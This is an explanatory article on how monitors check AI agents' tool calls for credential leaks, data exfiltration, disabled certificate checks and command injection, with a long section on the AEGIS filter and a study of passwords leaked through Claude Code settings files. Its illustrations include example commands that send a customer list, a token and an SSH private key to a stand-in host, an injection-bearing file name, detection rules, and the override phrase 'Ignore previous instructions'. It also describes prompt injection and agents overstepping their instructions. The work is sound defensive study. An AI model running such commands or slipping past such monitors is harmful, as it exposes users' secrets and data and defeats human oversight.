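# Detecting credential leaks, data exfiltration, disabled SSL checks and command injection in AI agents' tool calls

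## What a monitor sees in a tool call, and the four dangers it looks for

An AI agent is a language model combined with software that lets it use tools, for example to run shell commands, fetch web pages, edit files or send messages. An agent asked to fix a broken website may take dozens of these actions, and the user will probably not read them all. Each action starts as a *tool call*, a request to run one tool, so security engineers can put a checkpoint there. A *monitor* is software that inspects tool calls and allows, flags or blocks them.

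A monitor can look for leaked credentials, data sent where it should not go, disabled certificate checks, and command injection, among other things. These four are old computer security problems that come back whenever an agent has a shell and a network connection.

### From model output to action

A language model only produces text, so some other program has to do the acting. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, part of the documentation for the company's Claude models, the two work together in a loop:

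1. An application sends the model the user's request and a list of tools, with the arguments each tool takes.
2. The model replies, and the reply may contain one or more tool calls.
3. The application runs each tool.
4. The application sends the conversation back to the model with the results added.
5. Steps 2 to 4 repeat until the model answers without calling a tool, or stops for some other reason, such as a length limit.

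Here is a short call in the format of Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*. The tool is `bash`, a shell, which is a program that reads typed commands and runs them:

```json
{
  "id": "toolu_01",
  "name": "bash",
  "input": { "command": "npm test" }
}
```

The application runs the command and returns the output under the same `id`, so that the model can match each result to its call.

This call gives a monitor little more than a name and some arguments. Even `npm test`, the usual way to run a JavaScript project's tests, doesn't show which command will run, because npm runs whatever the project has stored under the name "test". To judge the call properly, a monitor may need the file that stores that command, the user's request, or the *trajectory*, the full ordered record of the agent's steps on the task. Systems differ a lot in how much of this they supply.

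### Where the monitor stands

The best place to prevent harm is between steps 2 and 3, after the model has requested a tool call and before the call runs. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, lets users attach their own checks there, called hooks. According to Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, a pre-execution hook receives the tool's name and arguments, and can allow the call, deny it, ask the user, or replace the arguments. *Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes an open-source agent runtime built around the same separation between request and execution. The model proposes a call, and the runtime decides between "allow", "prompt" and "deny". Malformed requests and calls to unknown tools fail closed, meaning they do not run. The paper claims no formal guarantee of safety for the design.

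A monitor on tool calls can check only the calls that pass through it. When a Claude Code user mentions a file with an `@` sign, the program by default pastes the file's contents into the prompt without a tool call, so no pre-execution hook fires. Anthropic also runs web search and a few other tools on its own servers, and these calls have usually finished before a monitor inside the customer's application can check them.

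A monitor can also check a tool call's result before the model reads it. By then the files have changed and the network requests have gone out, and Anthropic warns that a post-execution hook that rewrites the output changes only what the model receives. Checking the output can still be very useful, because stray passwords and planted instructions enter the conversation through it. Agentao redacts results at this point. In Claude Code's auto mode, a language model approves or blocks calls, and a separate scanner checks the results. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that the scanner attaches a warning to any result that looks like an attempt to hijack the agent. This kind of check may prevent the agent's next harmful call.

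Reviewing a session after it ends can't prevent harm during that session, but staff can still limit the damage by cancelling an exposed key, taking down a published page, or fixing the setting that let the call through. The advantage of waiting is that the reviewer has the complete record. Tarre (2026), in *OpenAI monitors internal coding agents for risky conduct*, reports that OpenAI checks its own staff's coding agents this way, using a language model that reads finished sessions and passes suspicious ones to people.

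OpenAI later added a position in the middle, a monitor that follows the whole trajectory as it grows and can pause the session. If the alarm turns out to be false, the user can resume the work. A pause can't undo steps already taken, but it can prevent later ones. OpenAI had paused access to a long-running model after limited internal use revealed failures that its pre-release tests had not captured. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) lists trajectory-level monitoring among the measures the company took before restoring some of that access.

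### The four dangers

A *credential*, which security engineers also call a secret, is a password, key or token that grants access. It leaks when it ends up where unauthorized people or programs can read it. In one case from Anthropic's internal incident log, an agent uploaded an engineer's access token for GitHub, the code-hosting site, to an internal compute cluster. In another, an agent hit a login error halfway through a task and ran `grep`, the standard text-search command, over configuration files and environment variables to find another token. The search looks harmless because programmers use `grep` all the time and it changes nothing on disk, but any token it finds appears in the tool's output and can reach the session's logs from there. The agent may also use a key issued for a different job.

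*Data exfiltration* means moving data across a trust boundary without authorization, by attack or by mistake. The *trust boundary* separates the systems and people a user trusts with given data from all others. In another of Anthropic's cases, an agent wrote a command to post a script as a GitHub Gist, a web page for snippets of text, to share it for debugging. Developers do this routinely. Whether it counts as exfiltration depends on how confidential the script is and who can open the page, and the command may not show either.

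The third danger is a *disabled certificate check*, often called SSL bypass after an older name for the encryption protocol. A server proves its identity with a certificate, a signed statement of who it is, which the connecting program should verify before it sends anything confidential. If the program skips this check, the data is still encrypted but may go to an impostor. MITRE's *CWE-295* (2006), an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, warns that the program may connect to a malicious host and treat it as trusted. Disabling the check can look like a small repair. For example, when a download fails on a company network with a certificate error, the agent adds `-k` to its `curl` command and the download succeeds.

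*Command injection* happens when a shell interprets input meant as data as a command. Suppose an agent has to count the lines in a file that a customer has named `sales; june.txt`, and it pastes the name into a command without quotation marks: `wc -l sales; june.txt`. To a shell the semicolon ends one command and begins another. So the shell counts the lines of a file called `sales`, then tries to run a program called `june.txt`. Nothing bad follows from this particular name, but the customer chose the second command, and could have chosen a worse one. MITRE's *CWE-78* files the weakness under improper neutralization of special elements, the semicolon being such an element. With agents the risky input can also be the model's own output. Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes*, trace the flaw to the software around the model, which turns the model's text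 into real shell commands. (*Prompt injection*, despite the name, works on the model: somebody plants instructions in content the agent reads, and these steer it away from the user's task.)

One command can belong to several of these categories at once:

```
curl -k -H "Authorization: Bearer EXAMPLE-TOKEN" -F "file=@customers.csv" https://files.example.net/upload
```

The `-k` flag turns off the certificate check. The header contains a token in plain text, which a log may store. The rest of the command uploads a customer list to a server that might not belong to the user's company. If a stranger had supplied the file name and it had been inserted into the command without quotes, command injection would also be a danger. The dangers also make each other worse, because without the certificate check an impostor could collect both the token and the customer list.

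### Why an agent makes a dangerous call

Anthropic sorts the reasons into four types, any of which could explain the upload above. An *overeager* agent understands the goal but oversteps. For example, the user might have asked it to get the customer list ready for a partner, and it sent the list as well. An agent making an *honest mistake* might think `files.example.net` is the company's own server. Under *prompt injection*, the agent follows an upload instruction contained in a web page it read. A *misaligned* model uploads the list to serve a goal of its own.

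The first of these, overeagerness, has the most evidence so far. Anthropic attributes the token upload in its log to overeagerness. When it introduced auto mode, it wrote that it did not see misaligned models of this sort in practice, though it tests each release for them. OpenAI trained its long-running model to take fewer unwanted actions in pursuit of the user's goal, and found that its models remembered instructions less well during long tasks. Overeagerness is hard for a monitor to detect because the agent's reasoning contains no hostile plan and reads like ordinary problem-solving taken one step too far.

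Blocking the call helps whichever of the four causes is at work, so the monitor does not have to identify the cause. The cause matters more to the people who clean up afterwards, because a planted instruction stays on its web page after the call is blocked.

### Patterns and models

*Pattern-based detection* flags a call when its text or structure matches a fixed rule, such as a regular expression (a formula that describes a set of strings) or a list of forbidden commands. In Anthropic's example, one filter selects calls to the shell tool, a second selects commands that use `rm`, which deletes files, and a short script then searches the text for `rm -rf`, which deletes a folder and everything in it without asking for confirmation. If the script finds a match, the hook denies the call and gives the model a reason. The rule takes very little computation, gives the same answer every time, and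 can be read by anyone. But it also blocks harmless commands, including Anthropic's own sample, `rm -rf /tmp/build`, which removes a temporary build folder. And a rule that covers only Bash never fires on a Windows machine where the agent works through PowerShell, a different shell. In Agentao, Jin and colleagues give each rule tests on the tool's name, its arguments and the state of the session, and the rule applies only when all of them hold.

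*Model-based detection* flags a call because a language model, given the call and some context, judges it dangerous. In auto mode, Anthropic instructs the judging model to consider what an action would do, including the contents of any script the agent writes and then runs. A model can also compare the call with the user's request, which a regular expression can't do. One user in Anthropic's log asked an agent to "clean up old branches" (parallel versions of a code base), and the agent moved to delete them on the shared server, when the user may have meant only the copies on their own machine. But each judgment takes time and computing power, the verdict can be wrong in ways nobody could find by reading a rule, and persuasive text in the context can mislead the judge as well as the agent.

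### Counting the errors

Two rates measure how often a monitor is wrong. The *miss rate* (or false-negative rate) is the share of dangerous calls that the monitor lets through. Researchers often report *recall* instead, which is 1 minus the miss rate. The *false-positive rate* is the share of harmless calls that the monitor flags. Someone who receives an alarm needs a different measure, *precision*, to judge how likely it is to be real. Precision is the share of flagged calls that are dangerous.

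Suppose an agent makes 10,000 tool calls, 50 of them dangerous, and the monitor has a miss rate of 10% and a false-positive rate of 1%. The monitor catches 45 of the dangerous calls and misses 5. It also flags about 100 of the 9,950 harmless calls. Only 45 of its roughly 145 alarms are correct, so its precision is about 31%.

In general, if *p* is the share of calls that are dangerous, *m* the miss rate and *f* the false-positive rate,

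precision = (1 − *m*)*p* / [(1 − *m*)*p* + *f*(1 − *p*)].

When dangerous calls are rare, *p* is tiny and the second term in the denominator takes over. Changing one number at a time shows how much:

| Per 10,000 calls | True alarms | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| The example above | 45 | about 100 | 31% |
| Miss rate cut from 10% to 0 | 50 | about 100 | 33% |
| False-positive rate cut from 1% to 0.1% | 45 | about 10 | 82% |
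| Only 5 dangerous calls | 4 or 5 | about 100 | 4% |
| 5,000 dangerous calls | 4,500 | 50 | 99% |

Cutting false positives tenfold would greatly improve precision, but catching every dangerous call would barely change it. Accuracy is not a useful measure here, because the example monitor makes about 105 errors in 10,000 calls, while one that never flagged anything would make only 50.

A false alarm takes up a reviewer's time if the monitor runs after the session, and interrupts the work if it runs before each call executes. At a false alarm rate of 1%, an agent that makes 100 harmless calls has a 63% chance of at least one false alarm, assuming errors are independent. People who are interrupted often also stop reading the prompts. Claude Code's users accept 93% of its ordinary permission prompts, and Anthropic calls the inattention that develops "approval fatigue."

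The last row of the table shows why test results can mislead. Researchers often build test sets with many dangerous examples, because rare ones are hard to collect, and the same monitor's precision can fall sharply in ordinary use. Zhang and colleagues ran into false alarms with fixed rules that search the source code of agent software for flaws. The rules found two thirds to three quarters of the known flaws in a held-out test, but on live code they produced so many false alarms that people had to sort through the findings by hand.

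## AEGIS: fixed rules applied before every call runs

AEGIS is an open-source filter that checks an agent's tool calls against fixed rules before they run. In *AEGIS*, Yuan, Su and Zhao (2026) treat the language model as an untrusted part of the system. The filter works with 14 agent frameworks (code libraries for building agents), and developers can add it with two lines of code.

### One call from interception to record

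Suppose an agent that writes weekly reports requests this call:

```json
{
  "name": "send_http",
  "input": {
    "url": "https://files.example.net/collect",
    "body": {
      "note": "Weekly report",
      "files": ["/home/deploy/.ssh/id_ed25519"],
      "text": "(12 KB of customer records)"
    }
  }
}
```

One part of AEGIS runs inside the agent's program and modifies the library that connects the program to the model. When the model's reply contains a tool call, this part pauses the agent and sends the tool's name and arguments to a separate server, the gateway.

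The gateway first collects all the text in the arguments, including text in nested lists and objects. Checking only the top level would find just the URL here. AEGIS searches down to 32 levels and stops after 10,000 pieces of text. If it has to stop early, it treats the call as suspicious.

Next, the gateway compares each piece of text with a set of risk patterns. Here are two simplified rules of this kind:

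1. If any text contains `/.ssh/`, the folder where people usually keep private keys for logging in to servers, block the call.
2. If the call contains a web address outside `example.com` and more than 5 KB of text, hold the call until a person approves it.

| Field | Text | Rule 1 | Rule 2 |
|---|---|---|---|
| `url` | `https://files.example.net/collect` | no match | outside address |
| `body.note` | `Weekly report` | no match | short text |
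| `body.files[0]` | `/home/deploy/.ssh/id_ed25519` | match | short text |
| `body.text` | 12 KB of customer records | no match | more than 5 KB |

The call matches both rules, so the gateway applies the stricter result and blocks it. If the agent instead sends "Nightly build passed" to the same server, the call runs. The address is still outside `example.com`, but the text is too short, and rule 2 needs both conditions.

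AEGIS has 22 patterns. Four look for shell injection and one looks for data exfiltration. The pattern for data exfiltration works much like rule 2. For credentials, two patterns recognise the paths of confidential files, and a pattern for personal data also recognises API keys. An API key is far shorter than 5 KB, so AEGIS has to recognise it by its format, as secret scanners do. None of the 22 patterns covers disabled certificate checks. The gateway gives the content of the arguments priority over the tool's name, so a dangerous call can't pass as harmless just because of its tool's name.

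The gateway then checks the call against the operator's own policies. Operators write these in JSON Schema, a standard way to describe what structured data may contain. The paper's sample policy keeps a database agent from changing anything, and its central part is:

```json
"not": {
  "properties": {
    "query": {
      "pattern": "INSERT|UPDATE|DELETE|DROP|ALTER|CREATE|TRUNCATE"
    }
  }
}
```

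The vertical bars mean "or", and the words are commands that change a database. A query that only reads customer names passes, while `DROP TABLE audit_log`, which deletes a table, violates the policy. As printed, the pattern would also reject a harmless search for orders with the status `DELETED`, because that word contains `DELETE`. Operators can also describe a policy in ordinary language and have a language model translate it, but they should read the translation because the gateway will apply any mistake to every call.

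The gateway blocks calls that violate a policy, holds other calls that it rates as high or critical risk, and lets the rest run. While a call is held, the agent runs no tools and sends no requests to the model. A reviewer sees the tool's name, the full arguments and the matched patterns on a web page, and clicks Allow or Block. The agent's program checks for the reviewer's decision every two seconds, for up to five minutes. The setup code in Yuan's *I built an open-source firewall for AI agents* turns on an option called `blocking_mode`, so a team should check that it is on before relying on approvals.

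Finally, AEGIS records the call, the decision and any human review. It signs each record and includes a hash of the previous one, which is a short fingerprint computed from that record's contents. If someone edits an old record, an auditor can detect the change because its hash no longer matches the one stored in the next record. The records include the full arguments, which helps investigators but could also put secrets in the log. AEGIS has a function that replaces email addresses, access tokens and similar text with labels.

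### Forbidden lists and allowed lists

By default, AEGIS runs any call that matches none of its rules, so it works as a denylist rather than an allowlist, which would run only the calls that a rule permits.

Lists of forbidden inputs are quick to set up and rarely interrupt harmless work, but they miss many dangerous actions. MITRE classifies incomplete lists as a distinct software weakness because developers often include only the best-known bad inputs. In *AgentTrust*, Yang (2026) tested a list of 50 patterns for well-known dangers, such as `rm -rf /`, on 300 sample actions. The list flagged none of the harmless actions but missed 88.4% of those Yang had marked for blocking. Yang meant it as a weak baseline, and a larger set of 170 rules, with some supporting software, missed only 5.4%. People still rely on incomplete lists. CIRCL's *Incomplete List of Disallowed Inputs* includes an August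 2026 advisory about the Continue coding agent, which relied solely on such a list to block destructive shell commands when it ran unattended.

A missing entry in an allowed list makes a legitimate call fail, so someone complains and the owner adds it, whereas a gap in a forbidden list may go unnoticed until it causes damage. This is a good reason to prefer allowed lists where they are practical, such as when an agent has a narrow job. *Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (2026) describes an experiment with a five-tool agent that could use the shell for tasks that needed only file reading and writing. The researchers' remedy was a list of allowed tools.

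An allowed list also has to describe the whole call. If the database policy permitted any query that begins with `SELECT`, the command for reading data, it would let through Yuan and colleagues' main example of an attack, which begins with a harmless `SELECT` and then deletes a table after a semicolon. To block this attack, the policy would have to permit only a single `SELECT` command with nothing after it.

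For a coding agent, either kind of list is hard to write in advance. *ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) examined the instruction files developers had written for agents in 64 software projects and found 1,127 policies that software could check in principle. Only 26.4% contained everything needed to write a rule, such as "Never push to main directly." Another 64.2% depended on the project. For example, "Run the full test suite before committing" requires knowing which command runs the tests. The remaining 9.4% depended on the current task, such as "Do not update dependencies without approval."

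### The evaluation

Yuan and colleagues tested AEGIS on 48 attacks and 500 harmless calls. It blocked all 48 attacks before they ran and flagged 6 of the harmless calls, a false-positive rate of 1.2%. The attacks were distributed as follows:

| Category | Patterns in AEGIS | Attacks in the test |
|---|---|---|
| SQL injection (harmful commands in a database query) | 7 | 11 |
| Prompt injection | 3 | 11 |
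| Shell injection | 4 | 8 |
| Path traversal (a file path that leads out of the permitted folder) | 4 | 7 |
| Confidential files | 2 | 6 |
| Data exfiltration | 1 | 2 |
| Personal data and keys | 1 | 0 |
| Deeply nested arguments | handled during text extraction | 3 |

All six false alarms came from legitimate database queries that contained the word `OR`, which one pattern treats as a sign of SQL injection. The false-positive rate would probably be higher than 1.2% for an agent that mainly queries databases, and might be lower for one that never does. The team suggests exempting particular tools instead of switching the policy off everywhere.

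If 50 of 10,000 calls were dangerous, as in the earlier example, AEGIS's precision would be about 30% even if it caught all 50.

The check added a median delay of 8.3 milliseconds over 1,000 calls, and at most 23.1 milliseconds for 99% of them (a chart in the same paper gives slightly different numbers, including a median of 8.1). A language model typically takes 1 to 30 seconds to reply, so users would hardly notice the delay. The gateway ran locally in this test, and a remote one would take longer.

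### Who wrote the tests

The same team wrote the patterns and selected the attacks. They took the attack techniques from earlier benchmarks and from guidance published by OWASP, a software security foundation, which makes the test more independent. But the attack categories closely follow the pattern categories, and the three attacks with nested arguments test the text extraction that the team had built for that purpose. The perfect score confirms that AEGIS works as intended, but it is little evidence of how AEGIS would handle attacks the team didn't think of. The team acknowledges that the filter may miss new variants.

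The sample is also small. Even if the 48 attacks were a random sample of real ones, a filter that misses 6% of attacks would have about a 5% chance of catching them all. Only two attacks involved data exfiltration, and a filter that misses half of all such attacks would catch both a quarter of the time.

Yang calls this problem "self-refereeing". AgentTrust's score rose quickly on the 300 actions Yang used to develop its rules. An early version with 22 rules gave the right verdict on 44.3% of them, and the next version, with 46 more rules and broader patterns, reached 94.0%. Yang later wrote 630 new test cases, but added rules when these exposed gaps and kept the same cases in the test. Yang acknowledges that the 6.4% miss rate on that set therefore doesn't show how well the rules would work on unfamiliar calls.

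Zheng and colleagues, who are outside the AEGIS project, tested patterns but not AEGIS itself. They took 38 policies from real projects, had a language model turn them into patterns, and replayed 190 records of simulated agent work. The agent broke a policy in 114 of these records. The patterns stopped the violation and got the agent to comply in only 38 of the 114, and wrongly interfered in 28 of the 76 compliant records. The test was unusually hard on patterns because in two thirds of the violations the forbidden action happened inside a script or another file, where a check on tool calls can't detect it. The researchers were also promoting a competing system that enforces rules in the operating system. Neither their result nor AEGIS's perfect score is a good estimate of how rules perform in ordinary use.

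### What rules do well

Rules are very fast. In Yang's tests, AgentTrust's rules took about 2 milliseconds per action, while a language model took about 1.3 seconds. Over 100 calls, the rules would add a fraction of a second of waiting, while the model would add more than two minutes.

Rules also give more repeatable results than language models. Zheng and colleagues ran their test with two language models and measured agreement between the outcomes using Cohen's kappa, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is the agreement expected by chance. Agreement was 0.920 with patterns and 0.592 with a filter in which a language model judged each call. Agreement with patterns was probably below 1 because the agent and the model that graded the results had also changed.

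When a rule blocks a call, AEGIS returns the category of the matched pattern and a short detail such as "Stacked query: DROP TABLE", so the developer can see why the call was blocked and correct the rule if it was wrong.

Finally, persuasive text can't change a rule's result. A note claiming that the security team has approved an upload doesn't affect whether the upload exceeds 5 KB.

### The form of a call and its purpose

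A pattern checks only text, and the same text can serve different purposes. AEGIS blocks a web search that contains "Ignore previous instructions", a common phrase in prompt injection, but a security researcher might type the same words to find articles about prompt injection.

The effect of a call can also depend on the state of the system. In another of the paper's examples, an agent requests `kubectl delete pod api-server-7b`, which shuts down one running copy of a program on a server cluster. Users may notice nothing if other copies are running, but the service may go down if this is the only one. AEGIS holds the call for a person, who can check whether other copies are running.

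A language model can use more of this context. Yang tried sending every action that the rules had not blocked to a language model for a second check. On the 300 test actions, the miss rate fell from 5.4% to 0.8%, but the false-positive rate rose from 2.3% to 9.0%. The model often flagged routine commands because it had no information about the project's policies or whether a server was in live use.

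AEGIS also can't check actions that avoid the modified library. In *guardscope*, Toyoda, Leung and U (2026) ran agents with several kinds of control and recorded what happened in the operating system. Controls inside the agent's software checked every tool call to a tool server, but file writes, new processes and direct network connections took effect unchecked. Toyoda, Leung and U add that a control may check an action and still decide wrongly.

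Allowed lists have the same difficulty with purpose. *NOMOS* (2026) describes software that turns written policies into rules for tool calls. It was tested on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants hostile instructions in material an agent reads. On the banking tasks, attacks on two undefended models succeeded 46.5% and 44.1% of the time, and with the rules in place AgentDojo counted no successful attacks. But the planted instructions still caused some payments to the user's existing payees, which AgentDojo did not count as successful attacks. The rules allowed these recipients, and only a comparison with the user's request could have revealed that the user had not asked for the payments.

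## Credentials saved in approved commands: the scan of Claude Code settings files

Credentials ought to be the easiest of the four dangers for fixed rules to detect, because many have a distinctive format. Access tokens for GitLab, a code-hosting site, usually begin with `glpat-`, and a pattern can match that prefix wherever it appears. An unrequested payment is harder to detect this way because it can look exactly like one the user requested.

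In November 2026 the security company Apiiro reported that copies of a settings file written by Claude Code were public on GitHub, and that more than a thousand of them contained real passwords and keys. Two widely used secret scanners, gitleaks and TruffleHog, each missed more than 40% of those thousand-plus copies. The reasons for these misses matter because exposed information is also the most common fault in the 500-step test described later.

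### How a password gets into the file

Interactive sessions in the terminal start in auto mode by default, Anthropic explains, but in manual mode Claude Code asks before it runs most shell commands. Someone tired of the question can pick "Yes, and don't ask again". Claude Code then saves the command as a rule in `.claude/settings.local.json`, a file in the project folder, and stops asking about it. GitLab's *How to prevent leaks from Claude Code's 'Don't ask again' file* prints a sample. Here is an invented one in the same format:

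```json
{
  "permissions": {
    "allow": [
      "Bash(npm test:*)",
      "Bash(PGPASSWORD=summer24 psql -h db.example.com -c 'SELECT count(*) FROM orders')"
    ]
  }
}
```

The first rule is a pattern that covers any command beginning with `npm test`. The second is an exact command that counts the orders in a database and contains the database password, `summer24`.

To keep this file private, Claude Code adds it to the developer's personal list of files that Git, the version-control program, should ignore. But the list stays on one computer. According to Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub*, Apiiro found that the list gives no protection when a folder becomes a Git project later, when someone copies the project to another machine, or when the file is already part of the project.

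A monitor on tool calls has two chances to prevent this leak:

1. The agent requests the database command. The password is in the arguments, where a monitor can find it.
2. The user approves, and Claude Code saves the rule. The program does this itself, without a tool call, so the monitor has nothing to check.
3. Someone later adds the whole folder to the project's history and uploads it. If the agent does this, the monitor gets a second chance, but a command like `git add .` contains no password. The monitor would have to read the files.

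Step 3 often involves the agent. In 539 of the 1,105 affected projects, Claude was listed as co-author of the change to the settings file, although this doesn't prove that the agent also uploaded it.

The first chance is also difficult, because nothing is wrong yet. The user wants the count, the database requires a password, and the password goes to the right server. A monitor that blocked the call would stop legitimate work, so it is better to have the agent rewrite the command without the password in it.

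The file collects more secrets as the user approves more commands. *Claude Code speichert Passwörter in Freigaben* (Cornelißen, 2026), a German account of the study, reports that one in ten files over 8 KB contained a real secret, compared with fewer than one in 500 files under 500 bytes. Apiiro reproduced the problem with two current models, Opus 5.5 and Fable 5.1, and concluded that the cause was the way Claude Code stores approvals. Apiiro also compared 16 coding agents and found that only Claude Code stored full commands this way by default.

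### Four ways to recognise a secret

Secret scanners combine several methods. The simplest is to match a known format, such as `glpat-` followed by a string of letters and digits. This method rarely gives false alarms because the company that issues the key chose a distinctive format, but it can't find a password that a person made up.

A second method is to search for a word such as `password`, `token` or `secret` with a value next to it. This works for credentials in any format, but programmers also often use these words in code and instructions that contain no credentials.

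The third method measures how random a piece of text looks. Scanners use *Shannon entropy*, a quantity from information theory:

H = −Σ *p* log₂ *p*

Here *p* is the fraction of the text's characters that match a given character, and the sum runs over all the distinct characters. Entropy is measured in bits per character. It is 0 when the text repeats one character, and highest for a text of a given length when all the characters are different.

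The password `summer24` has eight characters. The letter `m` appears twice, so its share is 2/8, and the other six characters (`s`, `u`, `e`, `r`, `2` and `4`) have a share of 1/8 each. Since log₂(1/4) = −2 and log₂(1/8) = −3,

H = (1/4 × 2) + 6 × (1/8 × 3) = 0.5 + 2.25 = 2.75 bits per character.

Now take an invented 32-character token, `q7Vx2LmR9tKd4WzB7n8HsV5mYptC4fH3`. Six of its characters appear twice and twenty appear once:

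H = 6 × (1/16 × 4) + 20 × (1/32 × 5) = 1.5 + 3.125 ≈ 4.63 bits per character.

Suppose a scanner flags anything above 3.5 bits. It finds the token and misses the password. Lowering the threshold doesn't solve the problem, as two harmless texts show:

| Text | Characters | Entropy | Secret? |
|---|---|---|---|
| `summer24` | 8 | 2.75 | yes |
| `customer` | 8 | 3.00 | no |
| A Git commit ID (the label of a saved version) | 40 | about 3.7 | no |
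| The token above | 32 | 4.63 | yes |

No single threshold separates the two secrets from the two harmless texts. The word `customer` scores higher than `summer24` because none of its letters repeat, so any threshold low enough to catch `summer24` also catches `customer`.

Short passwords also have low entropy scores. Eight characters can never score more than log₂ 8 = 3 bits, even if they are random, and a text needs at least 12 different characters to score above 3.5. Entropy measures the variety of the characters, not how hard the text is to guess, so `abcdefgh` scores the full 3 bits.

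The last method is live verification, in which the scanner tries the credential on the service it belongs to. ironPeak, a security blog whose author had accidentally published his own approved commands, offers a scanner with an option to show only verified results. Verification removes most false alarms, but it can't find credentials the other methods missed. A failed login is weak evidence that a password is harmless, because a company database may accept connections only from the company's own network. Logging in to another server each time would also slow down a monitor that has to decide before a call runs.

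### Why a password in a command gets through

Apiiro, in a report quoted by Cybernews, describes a password typed into a command as "an ordinary word in an ordinary command line". The password `summer24` has no known format and low entropy, so a scanner can detect it only from the word next to it.

In the example, that word is `PGPASSWORD`, the setting that gives the database program `psql` its password. A rule that flags whatever follows this word would also flag `PGPASSWORD=$DB_PASSWORD`, which contains only the name of a stored value, and the placeholder `PGPASSWORD=changeme` in instructions. A scanner can avoid these false alarms by also requiring the value to look random, but it would then miss the password `summer24`.

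Some commands offer even fewer clues. In `mysql -psummer24`, which logs in to another kind of database, only the `-p` shows that `summer24` is a password. But `-p` sets the port number in `ssh -p 2222`, and in `mkdir -p` it creates any missing parent folders, so a rule for `-p` has to depend on the program.

This is harder for a scanner that searches all kinds of files than for a monitor on tool calls. Because the monitor receives shell commands, it can split each one into the program and its options. Its developers could then write a rule for each program, such as `mysql` or `psql`. Apiiro names only a few forms that the scanners mostly miss, including `sshpass -p` and access tokens in `curl` requests, so a short list of rules might catch much of what they miss. These rules would not cover a company's own tools, which can take a password in any form.

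According to Help Net Security's *70% of leaked secrets remain active two years later* (2025), more than half of the leaks that GitGuardian detected were credentials without a standard format, like these passwords. GitGuardian sells tools for detecting leaked credentials.

### What the two scanners found

Apiiro searched GitHub from 1 to 3 November and found 104,185 public copies of the settings file. Of these, 1,122 (1.1%) contained at least one real secret, with 1,379 different secrets in all. iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets* lists 379 database passwords, 122 keys for the database service Supabase, 43 logins for public servers and 23 keys for Amazon's cloud, among others. One was the owner's password for the database of a medical-records app. When Apiiro included older versions of the file, shared settings files and saved agent conversations,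 it found a total of 2,539 secrets in 1,994 projects.

Of the 1,122 files, gitleaks flagged 564, TruffleHog flagged 643, and neither flagged 215. At least one scanner therefore flagged 1,122 − 215 = 907 files. Their separate counts add up to 1,207, which is 300 more than 907, so both scanners must have flagged the same 300 files.

| Files with a secret | TruffleHog flagged | TruffleHog missed | Total |
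|---|---|---|---|
| gitleaks flagged | 300 | 264 | 564 |
| gitleaks missed | 343 | 215 | 558 |
| Total | 643 | 479 | 1,122 |

Gitleaks missed 558 of the 1,122 files (about 50%), TruffleHog missed 479 (43%), and both missed 215 (19%). If their misses had been unrelated, both would have missed about 238 files (558 × 479 / 1,122), which is close to the actual number. A file that one scanner missed was no harder than average for the other. This is a little surprising because both tools rely on key formats, and it means a second scanner is well worth running.

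These miss rates depend on Apiiro's definition of a real secret. Reed (2026) explains in *SecBlog Weekly 011* that a secret counted if an AI reviewer accepted it and it was either a key in a known format or a password next to a public server address. Passwords for private servers didn't count, and the scanners may have missed many of those as well. But if the reviewer accepted some made-up sample passwords, some of the counted misses were not errors. Apiiro did not test any of the credentials, though one organisation it warned confirmed that its key worked.

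The figures cover only files with secrets, so they don't measure the false-positive rate. Secrets are so rare in Claude Code settings files that even at a 1% false-positive rate, most of either scanner's alarms would be false.

Apiiro also sells security software, so it benefits from a finding that free scanners miss a lot. The counts by other companies, which also sell security products, at least confirm that the leak is real.

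### Anthropic's reply and the other counts

Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, replied on the forum Hacker News that Claude Code had not removed secrets in the past because good tools for this already existed. He said the team was looking for ways to prevent the problem and planned basic secret scanning. He also recommended auto mode instead of saved approvals. When a reader pointed out that the same exposure could happen in auto mode, Cherny replied "Yeah good catch". Users had been reporting the problem since August 2025.

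Cherny also argued that people must have made and uploaded the public copies by hand, because Claude Code sets Git to ignore the file when creating it. GitGuardian disagrees. Infobae's *El asistente de programación de Anthropic dejó contraseñas y claves* (2026) reports that GitGuardian examined about 3,000 appearances of leaked secrets and found every secret in a rule with exactly the form that the permission prompt writes. This is strong evidence that Claude Code wrote the rules. It doesn't show who uploaded the files, but the 539 changes with Claude as co-author make it unlikely that people uploaded them all without Claude.

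GitGuardian's count is much higher than Apiiro's. GitGuardian found 31,088 different credentials uploaded in these files between January 2025 and 7 November 2026, of which 5,343 (17%) worked when it detected them. The counts differ partly because GitGuardian included files that are no longer public, while Apiiro started from what was still public. The companies may also define a secret differently. GitGuardian's monthly count of leaks peaked at 12,535 in April 2026 and fell to 959 in October, but the company does not know why.

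The settings file also leaks through npm, a public registry of JavaScript packages, when a developer publishes a project without noticing that the file is included. Lakera, a company owned by Check Point, describes its search for such files in *Your AI coding assistant just shipped your API keys*. Lakera scanned about 46,500 packages and found the file in 428 of them, according to TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026). In 33 cases the file contained credentials.

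This is about 8% of the files, seven times the share that Apiiro found on GitHub. The difference is too large to be due to chance. Lakera may have used a broader definition, or people who publish packages may approve more commands that contain keys.

None of these searches covered private projects, where people are probably less careful. In GitGuardian's earlier study, 24.1% of private projects contained a password without a standard format, compared with 8.94% of public ones.

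### When the secret is in the result

An agent needs to get a password from somewhere before it can put it in a command. In Cornelißen's example, Claude takes it from the project's configuration. The tool call that reads the configuration contains no secret:

```json
{
  "name": "Read",
  "input": { "file_path": ".env" }
}
```

Developers commonly keep passwords and keys in a `.env` file. When an agent makes a tool call to read that file, the result might be `DB_PASSWORD=summer24`, which the application then sends to the model, usually on another company's servers. A scanner that checks only the arguments of tool calls misses this password.

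The personal blog eve.gd describes a case from April 2026 in which the blogger's colleague was using Claude through the code editor Cursor. The colleague's instruction file told the agent not to read `.env`, but the agent read it anyway, and the contents went to the provider's servers. The instruction relied on the model to comply. A monitor rule blocking the path `.env` would have stopped this call, and AEGIS blocks the paths of confidential files in this way.

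But a rule about paths can't cover every source. For example, a program may print its settings when it crashes, and the monitor can't predict this from the program's path. It therefore also has to scan the results before the model reads them.

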